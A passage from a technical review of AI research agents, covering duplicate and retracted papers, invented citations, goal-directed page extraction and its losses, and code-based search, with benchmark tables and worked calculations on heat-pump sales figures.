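Many papers appear first as a preprint and later in a journal. If an index has a record for each version, an agent may mistake them for two studies that found the same effect. Duplicates also distort citation counts. *OpenAlex* (2025), a review of the OpenAlex index, gives the example of a *Nature* article with two records. One shows 3,729 citations, close to the 3,473 on the journal's site, and the other shows 66,550.

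Comparing DOIs, the permanent identifiers that publishers assign to papers, catches most duplicates that come from searching several indexes. It can miss preprints, because a preprint and its published version sometimes have separate DOIs (*How to build an Open Science Monitor based on publications?*, 2025). *Beyond coauthorship* therefore used another pass to merge records with similar titles, but only if the year and the authors' surnames also fitted.

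When matching records of the same paper, an agent's software should allow the publication years to differ a little. A preprint can precede the journal version by a year or more, and its title can change. Databases also date the same article differently: OpenAlex generally records the date it first appeared, while Scopus uses the date of the journal issue. For biology, Europe PMC and the *PreprintToPaper dataset* (2025) link preprints directly to their journal versions, which is safer than guessing from titles. The agent should record which version it read, since the authors may have corrected a figure between versions.

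### Retracted papers

Journals retract papers that turn out to contain serious errors or fraud, but the papers usually stay online. Language models rarely identify retracted papers. *Do Large Language Models know Which Published Articles have been Retracted?* (Thelwall, 2026) tested three models without web access on the titles and abstracts of 161 retracted articles. The models wrongly classed 82% to 88% of them as not retracted. They also wrongly classed 28 of 34,070 articles that had not been retracted as retracted.

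Training data helps to explain this. *Officially corrected errors persist in AI training data* (2026) examined peS2o, a large collection of scientific papers for training language models, and estimated that it contains about 12,000 retracted papers. For 79% of those in a checked sample, nothing in the collection mentioned the retraction.

Search access alone doesn't solve the problem. *Performance of AI Tools in Citing Retracted Literature* (Labenbacher, Niederer and colleagues, 2026) tested nine free AI tools with five questions about each of 15 retracted articles. ChatGPT 5 did best, answering all five correctly for eight articles. The three tools made for research, SciSpace, ScienceOS and Consensus, didn't get all five right for any article. The researchers suspect that these tools rely on databases that aren't updated often enough. The answers date from mid-2025, so current tools may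 do better.

Retractions are easy to look up. OpenAlex flagged 392 of the 397 retracted papers that the training-data researchers found in it. The software can check this flag for every paper before the agent cites it. However, all of these papers had been retracted for at least two years, so the flag may be less reliable for recent retractions. It would be wise to check Crossref and the Retraction Watch database as well.

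A retraction flag on one paper doesn't identify the other papers that rely on it. More than half of those 397 retracted papers had at least one citation from a year or more after the retraction. The researchers managed to check 24 of these citations. None mentioned the retraction, and 15 relied on the retracted results. If an agent's answer rests mainly on two or three studies, it should also check the papers that those studies depend on.

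*Dead Science Walking* (2026) proposes a score for how well a system handles retractions:

R = 1 − r / max(1, c)

where r is the number of retracted papers that the system cites as support without a warning, and c is the number of all citations that support a claim. A report with one such paper among 40 citations scores 0.975. That looks excellent even if the retracted paper is the only evidence for the main conclusion, so the score is more useful for comparing systems on disputed topics than for approving a particular report.

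### Papers that don't exist

Language models sometimes invent references, and people then publish them. Sakai, Kamigaito and Watanabe (2026), in *HalluCitation Matters*, found nearly 300 papers with at least one invented reference at three leading language-technology conferences in 2024 and 2025, most of them from 2025. *Detecting Hallucinated and Suspicious Citations* (2026) describes a study in *The Lancet* that found 4,046 invented references in 2,810 biomedical papers. The numbers are still small in some fields. *Testing Our Foundations* (2026) reports that they rose from 3 in 2025 to 17 in 2026 at one computing-education conference.

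These invented references can then get into the indexes. Google Scholar, for instance, creates entries for works it has found only in other papers' reference lists. *GhostCite* (2026) warns that invented references add nonexistent papers, and false links to them, to the citation network. An agent that follows references could reach such an entry, see that several papers cite it, and conclude that the work is well established.

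Agents also invent references themselves, though searching greatly reduces this. *MagTrace* (2026) scored citations on magnetic materials by whether the papers exist, fit the task and support the claim. The model scored 0.425 from memory and 0.867 as an agent with search. How often agents invent references depends heavily on the model. In the troponin test, five of seven agents invented none, but Qwen3.7-Plus invented 27 of its 60 references and got details wrong in another 31.

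To check a reference, the software can look up its DOI and compare the title, authors and year. When a language model suggests papers from the web, the system in *Distribird* similarly accepts them only after checking them against Semantic Scholar. The agent needs to see an abstract, a publisher's page or the text itself, because a bare index entry may have come from someone else's invented reference.

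A failed lookup doesn't prove that a paper is made up. OpenAlex has only 91 records from the *Journal of Machine Learning Research*, so most of that journal's recent articles could look fake if the software checked only there. The software should try at least one other index before it rejects a paper. Even a real paper may not support the claim it is cited for. When the *MagTrace* model worked from memory, 17% of its citations with a readable abstract pointed to real papers whose abstracts contradicted what it had written.

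## Reading a page for a stated goal

An agent usually has to open a study to find out whether it attributes heat-pump sales to subsidies. Full pages soon take up much of the context window, so many research agents use goal-directed extraction, in which an extractor returns only what is relevant to a stated goal. Tongyi's `visit` tool works this way. Extractors are usually smaller models than the agent's own.

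### From address to extract

In Tongyi DeepResearch's published code (Tongyi Lab, 2025), the `visit` tool uses two outside services. Jina fetches the page and returns its text. The other service is the extractor, which a developer chooses separately from the agent's own model.

Converting a web page to text removes most of its source code. According to *An Index-based Approach for Efficient and Effective Web Content Extraction* (Chen, Xu and colleagues, 2025), the source code of a median web page is about 223,000 tokens, but only about 9,000 remain without scripts and styling. A minority of pages keep real content inside their scripts, so a converter that deletes every script deletes that content too. For example, it could easily remove an interactive chart of heat-pump sales.

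Next, the `visit` code keeps only the first 95,000 tokens of the text. If the extractor returns nothing, the code cuts the text by 30% and tries again, up to three times, then tries once more with only the first 25,000 characters (about 6,000 tokens). The code never reports to the agent how much of the page the extractor processed.

The extractor's prompt contains just the page text and the goal. It asks for a JSON object with three fields:

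| Field | What the prompt asks for |
|---|---|
| `rational` | The sections or data that relate directly to the goal |
| `evidence` | The most relevant information, in its full original context as far as possible, even if that takes more than three paragraphs |
| `summary` | A concise paragraph that also judges how much the information contributes to the goal |

The software passes `evidence` and `summary` to the agent and discards `rational`. Other systems also use versions of this prompt. *G-ReAct* (2026) uses a lightly reworded version, and *Search More, Think Less* (2026) uses one that has the same three parts and asks for evidence as exact or minimally edited excerpts.

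When a page can't be fetched, the agent receives a message that the page's content could not be accessed. It receives the same message when the fetch succeeds but the extractor repeatedly writes invalid JSON, so it could give up on the best page it has found because of a syntax error.

Tongyi's technical report is inconsistent about goals, but the code also shows that the tool applies one goal to every page in the list. The page reader in *Traverse* (2026) similarly takes one question for one or more addresses, which the paper says supports comparison. For example, an agent could use one call to find units sold in 2021 and 2024 on five national statistics pages. An agent that needs different information from two pages should make two calls.

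### What extraction saves

If an agent opens thirty pages of 12,000 tokens each, the full pages would take up 360,000 tokens, and a 128,000-token context window would fill up during the eleventh page. Thirty extracts of 400 tokens each would take up 12,000 tokens, or about 9% of the window. Tongyi's prompt encourages longer extracts, but even at 1,000 tokens each, thirty would fit easily.

The extractor still has to read all 360,000 tokens, but it reads each page once, while the agent rereads its whole history every time it continues. A run with ten pages, one per turn, and 3,000 tokens of instructions would fit in the context window either way. If we ignore the agent's own writing, an agent with full pages reads about 693,000 tokens over that run. With extracts, the agent reads 55,000 and the extractor about 120,000, so the total is roughly a quarter as large, and a cheaper model does most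 of the reading.

Li, Wu and colleagues (2025), in *Nested Browser-Use Learning for Agentic Information Seeking*, tested whether this also improves answers. They gave GPT-OSS-120B, an open model from OpenAI, a browser and varied two things: whether the browser returned full pages or extracts, and whether the agent had a standard set of browser tools or a simpler set of four. These are the percentages of correct answers on GAIA, a test for general assistants, and XBench, a set of Chinese search questions:

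| Page content | Browser tools | GAIA | XBench |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full | Standard | 46.6 | 40.0 |
| Extracts | Standard | 60.2 | 61.0 |
| Full | Simple | 55.3 | 40.0 |
| Extracts | Simple | 73.8 | 71.0 |

Extraction added 14 to 31 points. The GAIA set had only 103 questions, but gains this large on both sets are unlikely to be luck. Extraction helps long runs most. In a separate test on BrowseComp questions, the agent had gone through more than 128,000 tokens of page content after about 20 tool calls. About 85% of its runs were still unfinished at that point and would have had to stop without extraction.

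### The price of leaving things out

An extractor can also drop the one fact the agent needs. If each needed fact survives extraction with probability q, and the losses are independent, an answer that needs m facts has all of them with probability

P = qᵐ

The heat-pump question needs sales figures for five countries in two years, so m is at least 10 before counting the population figures. An extractor that keeps 95% of the facts would deliver all ten sales figures only 60% of the time. To deliver them 90% of the time, it would have to keep 99%.

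Ross, van der Vegt and colleagues (2026), in *On the impact of retrieved content representations in RAG pipelines*, provide realistic values for q. They took 2,391 questions that a single Wikipedia page can answer, shortened or rewrote the pages in thirteen ways, and had a language model judge whether the page that contained the answer still supported it. The last two columns below apply the formula to some of their results:

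| What the answering model receives | Answer survives (q) | All of 3 facts | All of 10 facts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original text, up to 10,750 tokens | 98.6% | 96% | 87% |
| The half of the sentences most relevant to the question | 96.9% | 91% | 73% |
| A short summary written for the question by a 70-billion-parameter model | 95.2% | 86% | 61% |
| A 100-word snippet around the sentence that a ranking model prefers | 74.3% | 41% | 5% |
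| A 100-word snippet around the sentence that best matches the question's words | 52.8% | 15% | 0.2% |

The original text scores below 100%, perhaps because of the length limit or mistakes by the judge. Although the summaries averaged only 1.7% of the original length, one answering model was correct on 80.8% of the questions with them, compared with 81.3% with the original pages. Its accuracy fell to 60.7% with the word-matching snippets.

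In some cases, the formula underestimates the chance of getting every figure. If all ten sales figures are in one table, they will probably be kept or lost together, so the chance of getting them all is closer to q than to q¹⁰. An agent can also notice that a figure is missing and look elsewhere. If it finds a second page for each figure, with the same 95.2% chance that the figure is kept, the chance of losing a figure from both pages is 0.048², or about 0.2%, and the agent would get all ten 98% of the time. But it is difficult for the agent to notice that a figure is missing when it has never seen the page.

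### Passages the agent never sees

*Programmatic Search Agents* traced how much evidence is lost between the page and the agent, using runs by an agent based on DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash on questions from BrowseComp-Plus. Each search fetched documents, ranked them, and passed up to ten to an extractor with 0.8 billion parameters, which selected passages and didn't write summaries. Other models labelled which of the extractor's candidate passages supported the answer or a detail in the question, and found 370 across 92 questions.

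Of the supporting passages that reached the extraction stage, the extractor returned 41.4% at the first opportunity and another 15.9% in response to later searches. The remaining 42.7% never reached the agent. The agent saw none of the supporting passages for seven questions and all of them for 30.

Much of this loss occurred because the extractor returned only one passage per document, so it always lost one when a page had two useful passages. An extractor like Tongyi's, which can return several paragraphs, would probably lose fewer. The share of passages that did arrive, 57.3%, is not a suitable value for q in the formula above, because several passages can support the same fact and the agent doesn't need them all.

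The researchers then tested whether the missing passages mattered. They replayed 55 runs up to the first search in which the extractor had left out supporting passages. They continued each run twice, once with the original passages and once with one of them replaced by a supporting passage from the same page.

| What the original response contained | Runs | Correct with original passages | Correct after the swap | Later searches, original | Later searches, after the swap |
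|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No supporting passage | 30 | 63.3% | 80.0% | 10.7 | 3.9 |
| Some supporting passages | 25 | 88.0% | 88.0% | not given separately | not given separately |

The swap raised success by 16.7 points and cut later searches by 64% when the agent had seen no support. There was no net gain when the agent had already seen some support, though success was already at 88%, which left little room for improvement.

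The evidence is stronger for the drop in searches than for the rise in success. The 16.7 points equal five questions out of 30, all from the first of two batches of runs. In the second batch, which had only 11 such runs, success stayed at 72.7%, but searches still fell from 10.2 to 5.6. The researchers also chose the replacement passages knowing the correct answer, which no working extractor can do. The results are therefore closer to an upper bound on the gain from better passage selection than to an estimate of it. The paper's proposed solution is to let the agent write code that controls this selection.

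An overly strict extractor can increase token use. An agent that fails to recognize that it has found the right page keeps searching, in this case about seven more times. At 800 tokens of results per search, the figure assumed earlier for ten snippets, that adds about 5,500 tokens, which is more than the total length of a dozen 400-token extracts.

### Errors in written summaries

An extractor that writes its own text can omit facts too, or change them. In *MuninAI*, Fischer, Meiler and Elgeti (2026) describe a research assistant that answers questions from a research group's own collection of papers. Its first version summarised each retrieved passage to save tokens, and the summaries left out numbers needed to answer the questions. When the researchers supplied the full text instead, accuracy rose to 82% in a test and 86.4% under ordinary conditions. Their account of the change doesn't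 give the earlier accuracy, so the size of the improvement is unclear, but they considered it worth the extra tokens and removed the summaries.

The first fix tried was a better retriever, which increased the share of relevant papers in the top ten results from 44% to 73% but raised answer accuracy by only 7.5 points. The right paper had usually been among the candidates already, and the problem was in reading it.

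At least this failure was easy to notice. The model recognised that the number was missing and declined to answer. It would have had no such warning if the summary had contained the wrong number. Several kinds of change could slip through on a page of heat-pump statistics:

- The table's heading gives sales in thousands, and the summary reports "65 units".
- The page was published in 2024 but covers 2023, and the summary attaches the later year to the figure.
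- A note explains that the figures include air conditioners, and the summary leaves it out.
- The page has no figure for 2021, and the extractor supplies one from its training data.

Few experiments seem to count these errors separately. Ross and colleagues, for instance, checked whether the summary kept the known answer, but a summary could pass that test and still drop a qualification or add a false detail next to the answer. *Why Your Deep Research Agent Fails?* (2026) introduces a benchmark that checks for hallucinations throughout an agent's run, not only in its final answer, and counts omitting facts that the sources support as hallucination. Similar tests could measure the extractor's errors directly.

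A larger extractor improves accuracy, up to a point. Li and colleagues changed only the extractor in their agent and tested it on 100 BrowseComp questions. The agent got 24 right with a 4-billion-parameter extractor, 35 with a 30-billion-parameter one, and 36 with GPT-OSS-120B. Ross and colleagues found a similar pattern with summaries by Google's Gemma 3 models. One answering model scored 40% with no pages, 51% with summaries by the 1-billion-parameter version, 71% with the 4-billion one, and about 77.5% with both the 12-billion and the 27-billion ones. A very small extractor therefore loses too much accuracy to justify the compute it saves, but one as large as the agent's own model may be unnecessary. The best size probably depends on the pages, since Wikipedia articles are easier to read than statistical annexes.

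Cutting long pages causes another kind of loss. In the Wikipedia experiment, the limit of 10,750 tokens affected 8.4% of the pages, mostly those with long lists. This matters for questions about data, because the needed row may be near the end of such a list. Tongyi's limit of 95,000 tokens would have affected very few of these articles, but Li and colleagues report that pages can easily exceed 64,000 tokens and sometimes pass a million. A 300-page energy report, for example, could lose its most useful part if its national tables are in an annex.

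Summaries help in some settings. *ContextClaim* (2026) gave models background text for deciding whether a statement makes a checkable claim. In one test, raw extracts lowered accuracy, and having a language model summarise them first recovered most of the loss. Omitting a figure from the summary does little harm in this task because a classifier needs only the gist of the background, but a research agent that has to divide sales by population needs the exact figures.

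Software can catch some errors with little computation. It can check that every number and quoted sentence in the extract appears in the page text, which would expose an invented sales figure but not a missing footnote. Fischer and colleagues' reading agent must produce a supporting sentence before it answers, or else abstain. None of these checks helps if the page is wrong or contains text written to mislead the extractor.

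### Phrasing the goal

Tongyi's extractor doesn't receive the user's question or anything the agent has found so far. The agent has to include any context the extractor needs in the goal, such as the fact that another country's figures exclude air conditioners, or that the agent plans to subtract the 2021 figure from the 2024 figure.

Suppose one country's page has a table headed "Heat pumps sold, thousand units", with 40 for 2021 and 65 for 2024, and a footnote saying that the figures include reversible air conditioners from 2023 onwards. Here are two goals and what a competent extractor might return for each:

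| Goal | Possible extract |
|---|---|
| "heat pump sales 2024" | Sales reached 65 thousand in 2024. |
| "Number of heat pumps sold in 2021 and in 2024. Copy the figures with their unit, the types of heat pump they include, and any footnote or change of method. If a year is missing, say so." | Heat pumps sold, thousand units. 2021: 40. 2024: 65. Footnote: from 2023, figures include reversible air conditioners. |

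The first extract is accurate but nearly useless. The agent would have to open the page again for the 2021 figure and would then calculate a rise of 25,000, with no indication that the change in counting could explain some or all of it. The longer goal adds perhaps 40 tokens and prevents both problems.

A goal can also be too leading. "Find evidence that subsidies increased heat-pump sales" can lead the extractor to skip a paragraph in which the researchers found no effect. A prompt for text that supports the goal, like the one in *Search More, Think Less*, may make this worse. A neutral goal would be "Find what the researchers concluded about subsidies, their evidence, and their reservations."

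A goal can't cover everything the agent doesn't yet know to ask about. The page reader in *SimpleSearch-VL* (2026) addresses this by summarising the page's main points as well as anything relevant to the goal. The agent may then notice, for example, that the page covers only newly built homes. But the summary can have only five sentences, which leaves little room for a table. The agent's own model writes the summary, so a developer doesn't need to run a separate extractor.

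Keeping a record of the goal also helps developers diagnose wrong answers, because they can see whether the agent asked for the wrong thing or the extractor failed to find what the agent asked for. The responses of Qianwen's commercial extraction service, documented in *Web scraping*, list each extraction with its goal and output.

### Other ways to read a page

An extractor can return passages from a page without generating their text. In the index-based method of Chen and colleagues, software splits the page into numbered blocks, and the model returns only the numbers of the relevant ones, such as blocks 3 to 5. The software then copies those blocks from the page, so the model can't invent or alter a figure, although it can still choose the wrong blocks.

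This is also fast, because the model writes very little. A 4-billion-parameter model trained for the method took 3.4 seconds per page, compared with 11.0 seconds for an ordinary model of the same size that wrote out its extracts. Answers based on the trained model's extracts scored 55.4 on a 100-point scale of word overlap with the correct answer, against 51.7 for the ordinary model. Most of that gain came from the training, since the ordinary model scored 52.8 when it returned block numbers. Copying whole blocks should make lost context less likely, though a table's unit may still be in a heading that the model didn't select.

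Searching within the page takes even less compute when it doesn't use a language model. The browsing tool in *Lost in the Maze* (2025) splits a page into pieces and returns the one that shares the longest sequence of words with the agent's query, up to 10,000 characters. This works well when the agent knows the page's wording, for instance when checking a quotation or finding a named table, but badly when the query uses "sales" and the page uses "shipments". The word-matching snippets in Ross and colleagues' experiment lost nearly half the answers, although the snippets were only about 100 words long and larger pieces would lose fewer.

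Very long documents call for reading in segments. Li and colleagues' extractor goes through a page one segment at a time and adds whatever serves the goal to a temporary workspace:

W ← W ∪ f(Pᵢ, g)

where W is the workspace, Pᵢ is the i-th segment, g is the goal and f is the extractor. The agent receives W after the last segment. Nothing is lost to a length limit, but the extractor has to read everything. A million-token document in segments of 30,000 tokens takes 34 extractor calls, and a table that runs across two segments may be separated from its heading. Software can reduce that risk by repeating the heading at the start of each segment. *WebChallenger* (2026) follows the page's own sections instead, and for a long table or list it first has the model pick the relevant items from each group, then extracts information only from those.

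The agent can also read the full page. This may be the most accurate and quickest choice for a few short pages. In Ross and colleagues' tests, the answering model processed five original pages in about 9 seconds. Summarising the pages first, one after another, raised the total to about 59 seconds. Running the summaries in parallel or using a smaller extractor would narrow the gap.

| Method | Main cost | Main weakness | When it is worth using |
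|---|---|---|---|
| Written extract | One model call per page | Can drop or change details | Screening many candidate pages |
| Verbatim passages by number | One short model call per page | Can separate a figure from its heading | Collecting figures and quotations |
| Search within the page | Almost none | Misses different wording | Finding a known phrase or table |
| Reading in segments | Many model calls for a long document | Can split a table or an argument | Long reports that exceed the length limit |
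| Full page | Up to the page's whole length in the agent's window | Crowds out later work | The few sources that decide the answer |

An agent can combine these methods on one question. For heat pumps, it might use written extracts to screen thirty pages, copy the sales tables verbatim, and read the full results sections of the two most important subsidy studies. Even reading both studies in full, at 12,000 tokens each, would use less than a fifth of a 128,000-token window. The software should save the text of every page it fetches so the agent can reread it for a new goal without downloading it again.

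## Running code, and calling the other tools from code

By this stage of the heat-pump question, the agent has sales figures for five countries in two years. It still has to divide them by population, subtract and rank, which it can do with a short Python program in the sandbox. If the tool returns error messages as well as printed output, the model can fix a misspelled name and run the code again. Newer designs also let the code call the search and page-reading tools.

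### Sales per head in a few lines

This program works out heat-pump sales per thousand people from invented figures. Each pair of numbers is the units sold and the population.

```python
data = {
    "A": {2021: (40_000, 5_400_000), 2024: (65_000, 5_600_000)},
    "B": {2021: (90_000, 38_000_000), 2024: (200_000, 37_500_000)},
    "C": {2021: (150_000, 83_200_000), 2024: (190_000, 83_500_000)},
    "D": {2021: (120_000, 10_400_000), 2024: (150_000, 10_600_000)},
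    "E": {2021: (380_000, 59_200_000), 2024: (350_000, 59_000_000)},
}
for country, d in data.items():
    old, new = (1000 * d[y][0] / d[y][1] for y in (2021, 2024))
    print(country, f"{old:.2f} {new:.2f} {new - old:+.2f} {new / old - 1:+.0%}")
```

It prints five lines, shown here as a table:

| Country | 2021 | 2024 | Rise | Growth |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | 7.41 | 11.61 | +4.20 | +57% |
| B | 2.37 | 5.33 | +2.96 | +125% |
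| C | 1.80 | 2.28 | +0.47 | +26% |
| D | 11.54 | 14.15 | +2.61 | +23% |
| E | 6.42 | 5.93 | −0.49 | −8% |

Country A comes first in extra units per thousand people and country B in percentage growth.

A strong model could probably do these ten divisions correctly in text, but the program records the figures behind the answer and would work just as well for five hundred rows. A few more lines could check the data, for instance by comparing the sum of a country's regional sales with its national total.

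Some interpreters keep variables from one call to the next, so the model can correct one figure in a table with a single line of code and rerun the calculation. Otherwise, it has to write out the whole table again, which uses more tokens and risks copying a number wrongly. In the setup described in *Programmatic tool calling*, part of Anthropic's documentation for its Claude models, each request gets a new sandbox unless the developer's software sends back the identifier of an earlier one. If the software omits the identifier, the model's next line of code may refer to a table that no longer exists.

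### Tests with and without an interpreter

An interpreter helps most when a problem needs long, exact calculations. *Measuring LLM Tool-Use Efficiency in Cryptographic Capture-the-Flag Competitions* (Iordache, 2026), a bachelor's thesis, tested three models on 15 code-breaking puzzles, with three attempts at each. The models succeeded in 7 of 135 attempts (5%) when they could only reason in text, and in 58 (43%) when they could run Python with its standard library. Iordache deliberately chose puzzles that tools were likely to help with. Many involved RSA, an encryption method that uses exact arithmetic on very long numbers.

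When the models could also install packages and command-line programs, their total successes fell from 58 to 53. One puzzle improved from 1 success in 9 attempts to 8 in 9, because the models could install a library with a ready-made function for finding the next prime number. On the other 14 puzzles, successes fell from 57 to 45. Most of that loss came from Claude 4.5 Haiku, a small model, while a version of Grok 4.1 built for longer reasoning improved slightly. Weaker models may waste much of a five-minute time limit on setting up their tools, though fifteen puzzles are too few to be sure.

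On ordinary mathematics problems, an interpreter made much less difference. Li, Song and colleagues (2026), in *TIDE-Bench*, tested eight systems with and without code on 500 problems from each of three sets. GSM8K consists of school word problems, MATH of competition problems and Omni-MATH of olympiad-level ones. These are the percentages of correct answers for four of the systems:

| Model | GSM8K, without → with | MATH, without → with | Omni-MATH, without → with |
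|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 94.2 → 94.8 | 98.6 → 97.8 | 68.4 → 60.0 |
| GPT-5 | 94.8 → 94.0 | 98.4 → 98.8 | 63.8 → 64.6 |
| Qwen3-32B | 89.2 → 87.4 | 96.8 → 88.0 | 34.8 → 32.0 |
| Qwen3-4B | 89.6 → 86.8 | 93.8 → 92.0 | 30.8 → 35.8 |

The stronger models had little room to improve on the two easier sets. They had more room on Omni-MATH, but the average over all eight systems fell by about half a point, and GPT-5.4 lost 8.4 points, which is unlikely to be due to chance. The researchers argue that code helps only if the model first turns the problem into a correct procedure. That is usually the hard part of an olympiad problem, whereas the procedure for an RSA puzzle may be well known and the arithmetic infeasible by hand.

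The procedure and arithmetic of the heat-pump calculation are both easy, so an interpreter would add little accuracy. Choosing the right figures to put into it is harder.

### Code that runs and gives the wrong answer

A program built on a wrong assumption runs without an error message to show the model that something went wrong. Suppose country A began counting reversible air conditioners in 2023, and they make up 20,000 of its 65,000 units in 2024. Excluding them lowers its rise from 4.20 units per thousand people to 0.63, which moves country A from first place to third and puts country B first on both measures. The code is the same in either case, so running it again or asking another model to check the syntax wouldn't reveal the problem.

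Mixed units are another common problem. If country A's table is in thousands and the model enters 40 and 65, the program prints a rise of +0.00 and puts A fourth. The growth column still shows +57%, because the missing factor of a thousand cancels out, so a model that prints only percentages would get the right growth figure and miss the mistake. One line of code can catch it by stopping the program if any country's sales fall outside, say, 0.1 to 50 units per thousand people. But a range check can't detect the air conditioners, since 65,000 is a plausible number.

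A model can write correct code and still not receive the result. In a data-analysis notebook, putting a variable's name on the last line displays its value. In an ordinary script, the same line displays nothing, so a model that writes notebook-style code for a tool like Tongyi's receives empty output, which it can easily misread as "no matching data". If the interpreter doesn't keep variables between calls, the model has to resend the whole program to add a print command.

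The model can also miscopy figures from an observation into its code. Ten numbers are manageable, but errors are more likely with a table of monthly figures for fifty regions. Anthropic pointed out in November 2025 that models may make more copying errors between tool calls when documents are large or have a complex structure. If the program can fetch the table itself, the model doesn't have to copy the figures.

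### Searching from inside a program

In programmatic search, the sandbox gives the model's code functions for searching and reading pages. The model writes a program that calls them, and it receives only what the program chooses to return. Here is a simplified program for the sales figures:

```python
pages = {}
for c in countries:
    hits = fuse(search_many([f"{c} heat pump sales 2021 2024",
                             f"{c} heat pump market units sold"]))
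    hits = [h for h in hits if h.domain not in shops]
    pages[c] = fetch_many([h.url for h in hits[:3]])
    rows = extract_many(pages[c], goal)
    print(c, len(hits), [(r.year, r.units, r.includes) for r in rows])
```

For each country, the program runs two wordings of the same query, merges the two lists of results, removes online shops, fetches the best three pages and uses an extractor to pull out the figures. A faster version would send all ten searches at once.

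In a conventional agent, the model receives the search results, chooses pages, requests them and reads the extracts, and the software waits for the model at each step. Most of these pauses are unnecessary. Once the model has decided to remove shops and open the top three pages, the software can do both as soon as the results arrive. *Programmatic Search Agents* separates two kinds of dependency between steps. A program can run steps in sequence when each only needs data from the one before, but it has to stop and return output to the model when the model must interpret the results before the next step.

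Calling tools from code can save many tokens. Under the earlier assumptions of 80 tokens per search result, 400 per extract and 3,000 for the instructions and question, a step-by-step agent reads 3,000 tokens, then 11,000 once the hundred search results are added, then 17,000 once the fifteen extracts are added, for a total of 31,000. If the program prints 600 tokens, the programmatic agent reads 3,000 and then 3,600, for a total of 6,600. Neither total includes the model's own writing, and the extractor reads the same fifteen pages either way.

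Programs can also run some queries that depend on earlier results. To find subsidy studies on the country with the largest rise, a program can calculate the rises, pick the largest and put that country's name into the next query. This is safe only if the five national figures count the same things. The model has to judge that from the footnotes, so it would be better to print the figures first and search for the studies in a second program.

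The same goes for a question about who founded the company that makes Poland's best-selling heat pump. An extractor could return the company's name, and the program could then search for its founder. But if the extractor picked the wrong company, every later search would be about that company, and the model might receive only a final answer, with no sign of the error.

### From CodeAct to Search as Code

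Yang, Yu and Desell (2026) trace the history of the approach in *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?* Two early methods, PAL and Program-of-Thoughts, had models write Python to solve arithmetic and symbolic problems. In 2024, CodeAct extended this to an agent's actions, so the model wrote executable Python instead of JSON tool calls. By 2025, BrowseMaster was running its searches this way.

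Anthropic's November 2025 article is about agents connected to many outside services through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for such connections. In one example, an agent copies the transcript of a two-hour meeting from one service to another. With ordinary tool calls, the whole transcript passes through the model twice, which could add 50,000 tokens, but code can copy it without putting it in the context window. The article also estimates that an agent could use 2,000 tokens instead of 150,000 if it loaded only the tool definitions it needed. This estimate is an illustration, and the saving doesn't carry over to a research agent with four or five tools, because their definitions are already short.

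According to *Programmatic tool calling*, when the model's code reaches a tool call, the code pauses and Anthropic's service requests the result from the developer's software, which has about four minutes to reply. The result goes to the paused code, not to the model, and the code continues. When the code finishes, the model receives the final output.

In February 2026, Anthropic applied this to web search. Claude could now write code that filtered search results and pages before they reached its context window. Anthropic's *Increase web search accuracy and efficiency with dynamic filtering* (2026) gives these scores for two models of the time:

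| Benchmark | Model | Basic search | Search with filtering code |
|---|---|---|---|
| BrowseComp, accuracy | Sonnet 4.6 | 33.3% | 46.6% |
| BrowseComp, accuracy | Opus 4.6 | 45.3% | 61.6% |
| DeepSearchQA, F1 | Sonnet 4.6 | 52.6% | 59.4% |
| DeepSearchQA, F1 | Opus 4.6 | 69.8% | 77.3% |

DeepSearchQA requires complete sets of answers. F1 combines the share of the agent's answers that are correct with the share of all correct answers that the agent found.

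The average gain was 11 points, with 24% fewer input tokens. When Anthropic weighted the tokens by price, the cost fell for Sonnet 4.6 but rose for Opus 4.6, probably because Opus wrote more code and providers charge more for output tokens than for input tokens. The comparison may also overstate the benefit of the filtering code. Anthropic says a basic search agent reads full web pages, so an ordinary extractor like the one in Tongyi's `visit` tool might have produced part of the same gain.

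Filtering by code has since become the default in Anthropic's newer web search tools. *Reproduce Claude's agentic search benchmark scores in the Messages API* (Li, 2026) gives the setup behind the company's benchmark scores. The model can call only the code tool directly, so it has to search and fetch pages from inside its code. One sample question asks which chief executive among the four largest US banks had held the post longest as of early 2024. Claude Sonnet 5 answered it correctly in 56 seconds, using four programs. A hard question can involve more than fifty page fetches, and without code the text of every page would enter the context window.

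The search company Perplexity introduced its own version, Search as Code, in June 2026. *Perplexity's "Search as Code" lets AI models write their own search pipelines* (The Decoder, 2026) describes three layers. The model plans the search and writes a Python script, a sandbox runs the script, and a library gives the script separate functions for parts of Perplexity's search engine, such as retrieving, filtering and reranking. A standard search service performs all those steps in a fixed order and lets the agent change only the query.

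Perplexity demonstrated the system on 200 critical software vulnerabilities. For each one, the agent had to find the vendor's own advisory, the affected product and the version that fixed the problem. Its script ran searches suited to each vendor's bulletin format, searched again to fill any gaps, and then checked that the vulnerability, product and version matched. According to Perplexity, this used 85% fewer tokens than its standard system. The company also measured gains on five benchmarks, from 5.5 points on BrowseComp to 19.8 on DeepSearchQA.

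These are all the company's own figures, and the 85% comes from a single task that suits code unusually well because it has two hundred similar items with the same fields to fill in. Using code would save much less on the subsidy part of the heat-pump question, because the agent has to read each study's argument.

### Three interfaces compared

*Programmatic Search Agents* provides a more controlled test. The researchers ran the same five models on BrowseComp-Plus with three interfaces, all using the same retriever, reranker and extractor:

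- With the query interface, the model could send several queries at once, and a fixed procedure turned each one into a list of passages.
- With the step-by-step interface, the model called five functions itself (retrieve, filter, rerank, extract and remove duplicates), but reranking the results of a retrieval, or extracting from the reranked list, required another turn.
- With the program interface, the model could combine the same five functions in one short program, with loops and conditions.

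The step-by-step and program interfaces both kept earlier results in a workspace for reuse. Each model could take up to 50 turns. These are the percentages of the 830 questions that each model answered correctly:

| Model | Queries | Step by step | Programs |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 54.94 | 57.71 | 62.29 |
| GLM-5.3-Flash | 44.94 | 47.11 | 51.08 |
| Qwen3.8-Flash | 33.37 | 23.25 | 48.43 |
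| GPT-5.6-Luna | 48.67 | 52.89 | 52.41 |
| Hunyuan-4-Preview | 57.57 | 59.65 | 63.06 |
| Average | 47.90 | 48.12 | 55.45 |

Without Qwen3.8-Flash, the average score rises from 51.5% to 54.3% when models can call the functions separately, and to 57.2% when they can combine them in a program, so control over the functions and the ability to combine them contributed about equally. Including Qwen hides almost all of the average gain from separate calls, because it lost 10 points with them while each of the other models gained between 2 and 4. GPT-5.6-Luna got four fewer questions right with programs than with separate calls, which is effectively a tie.

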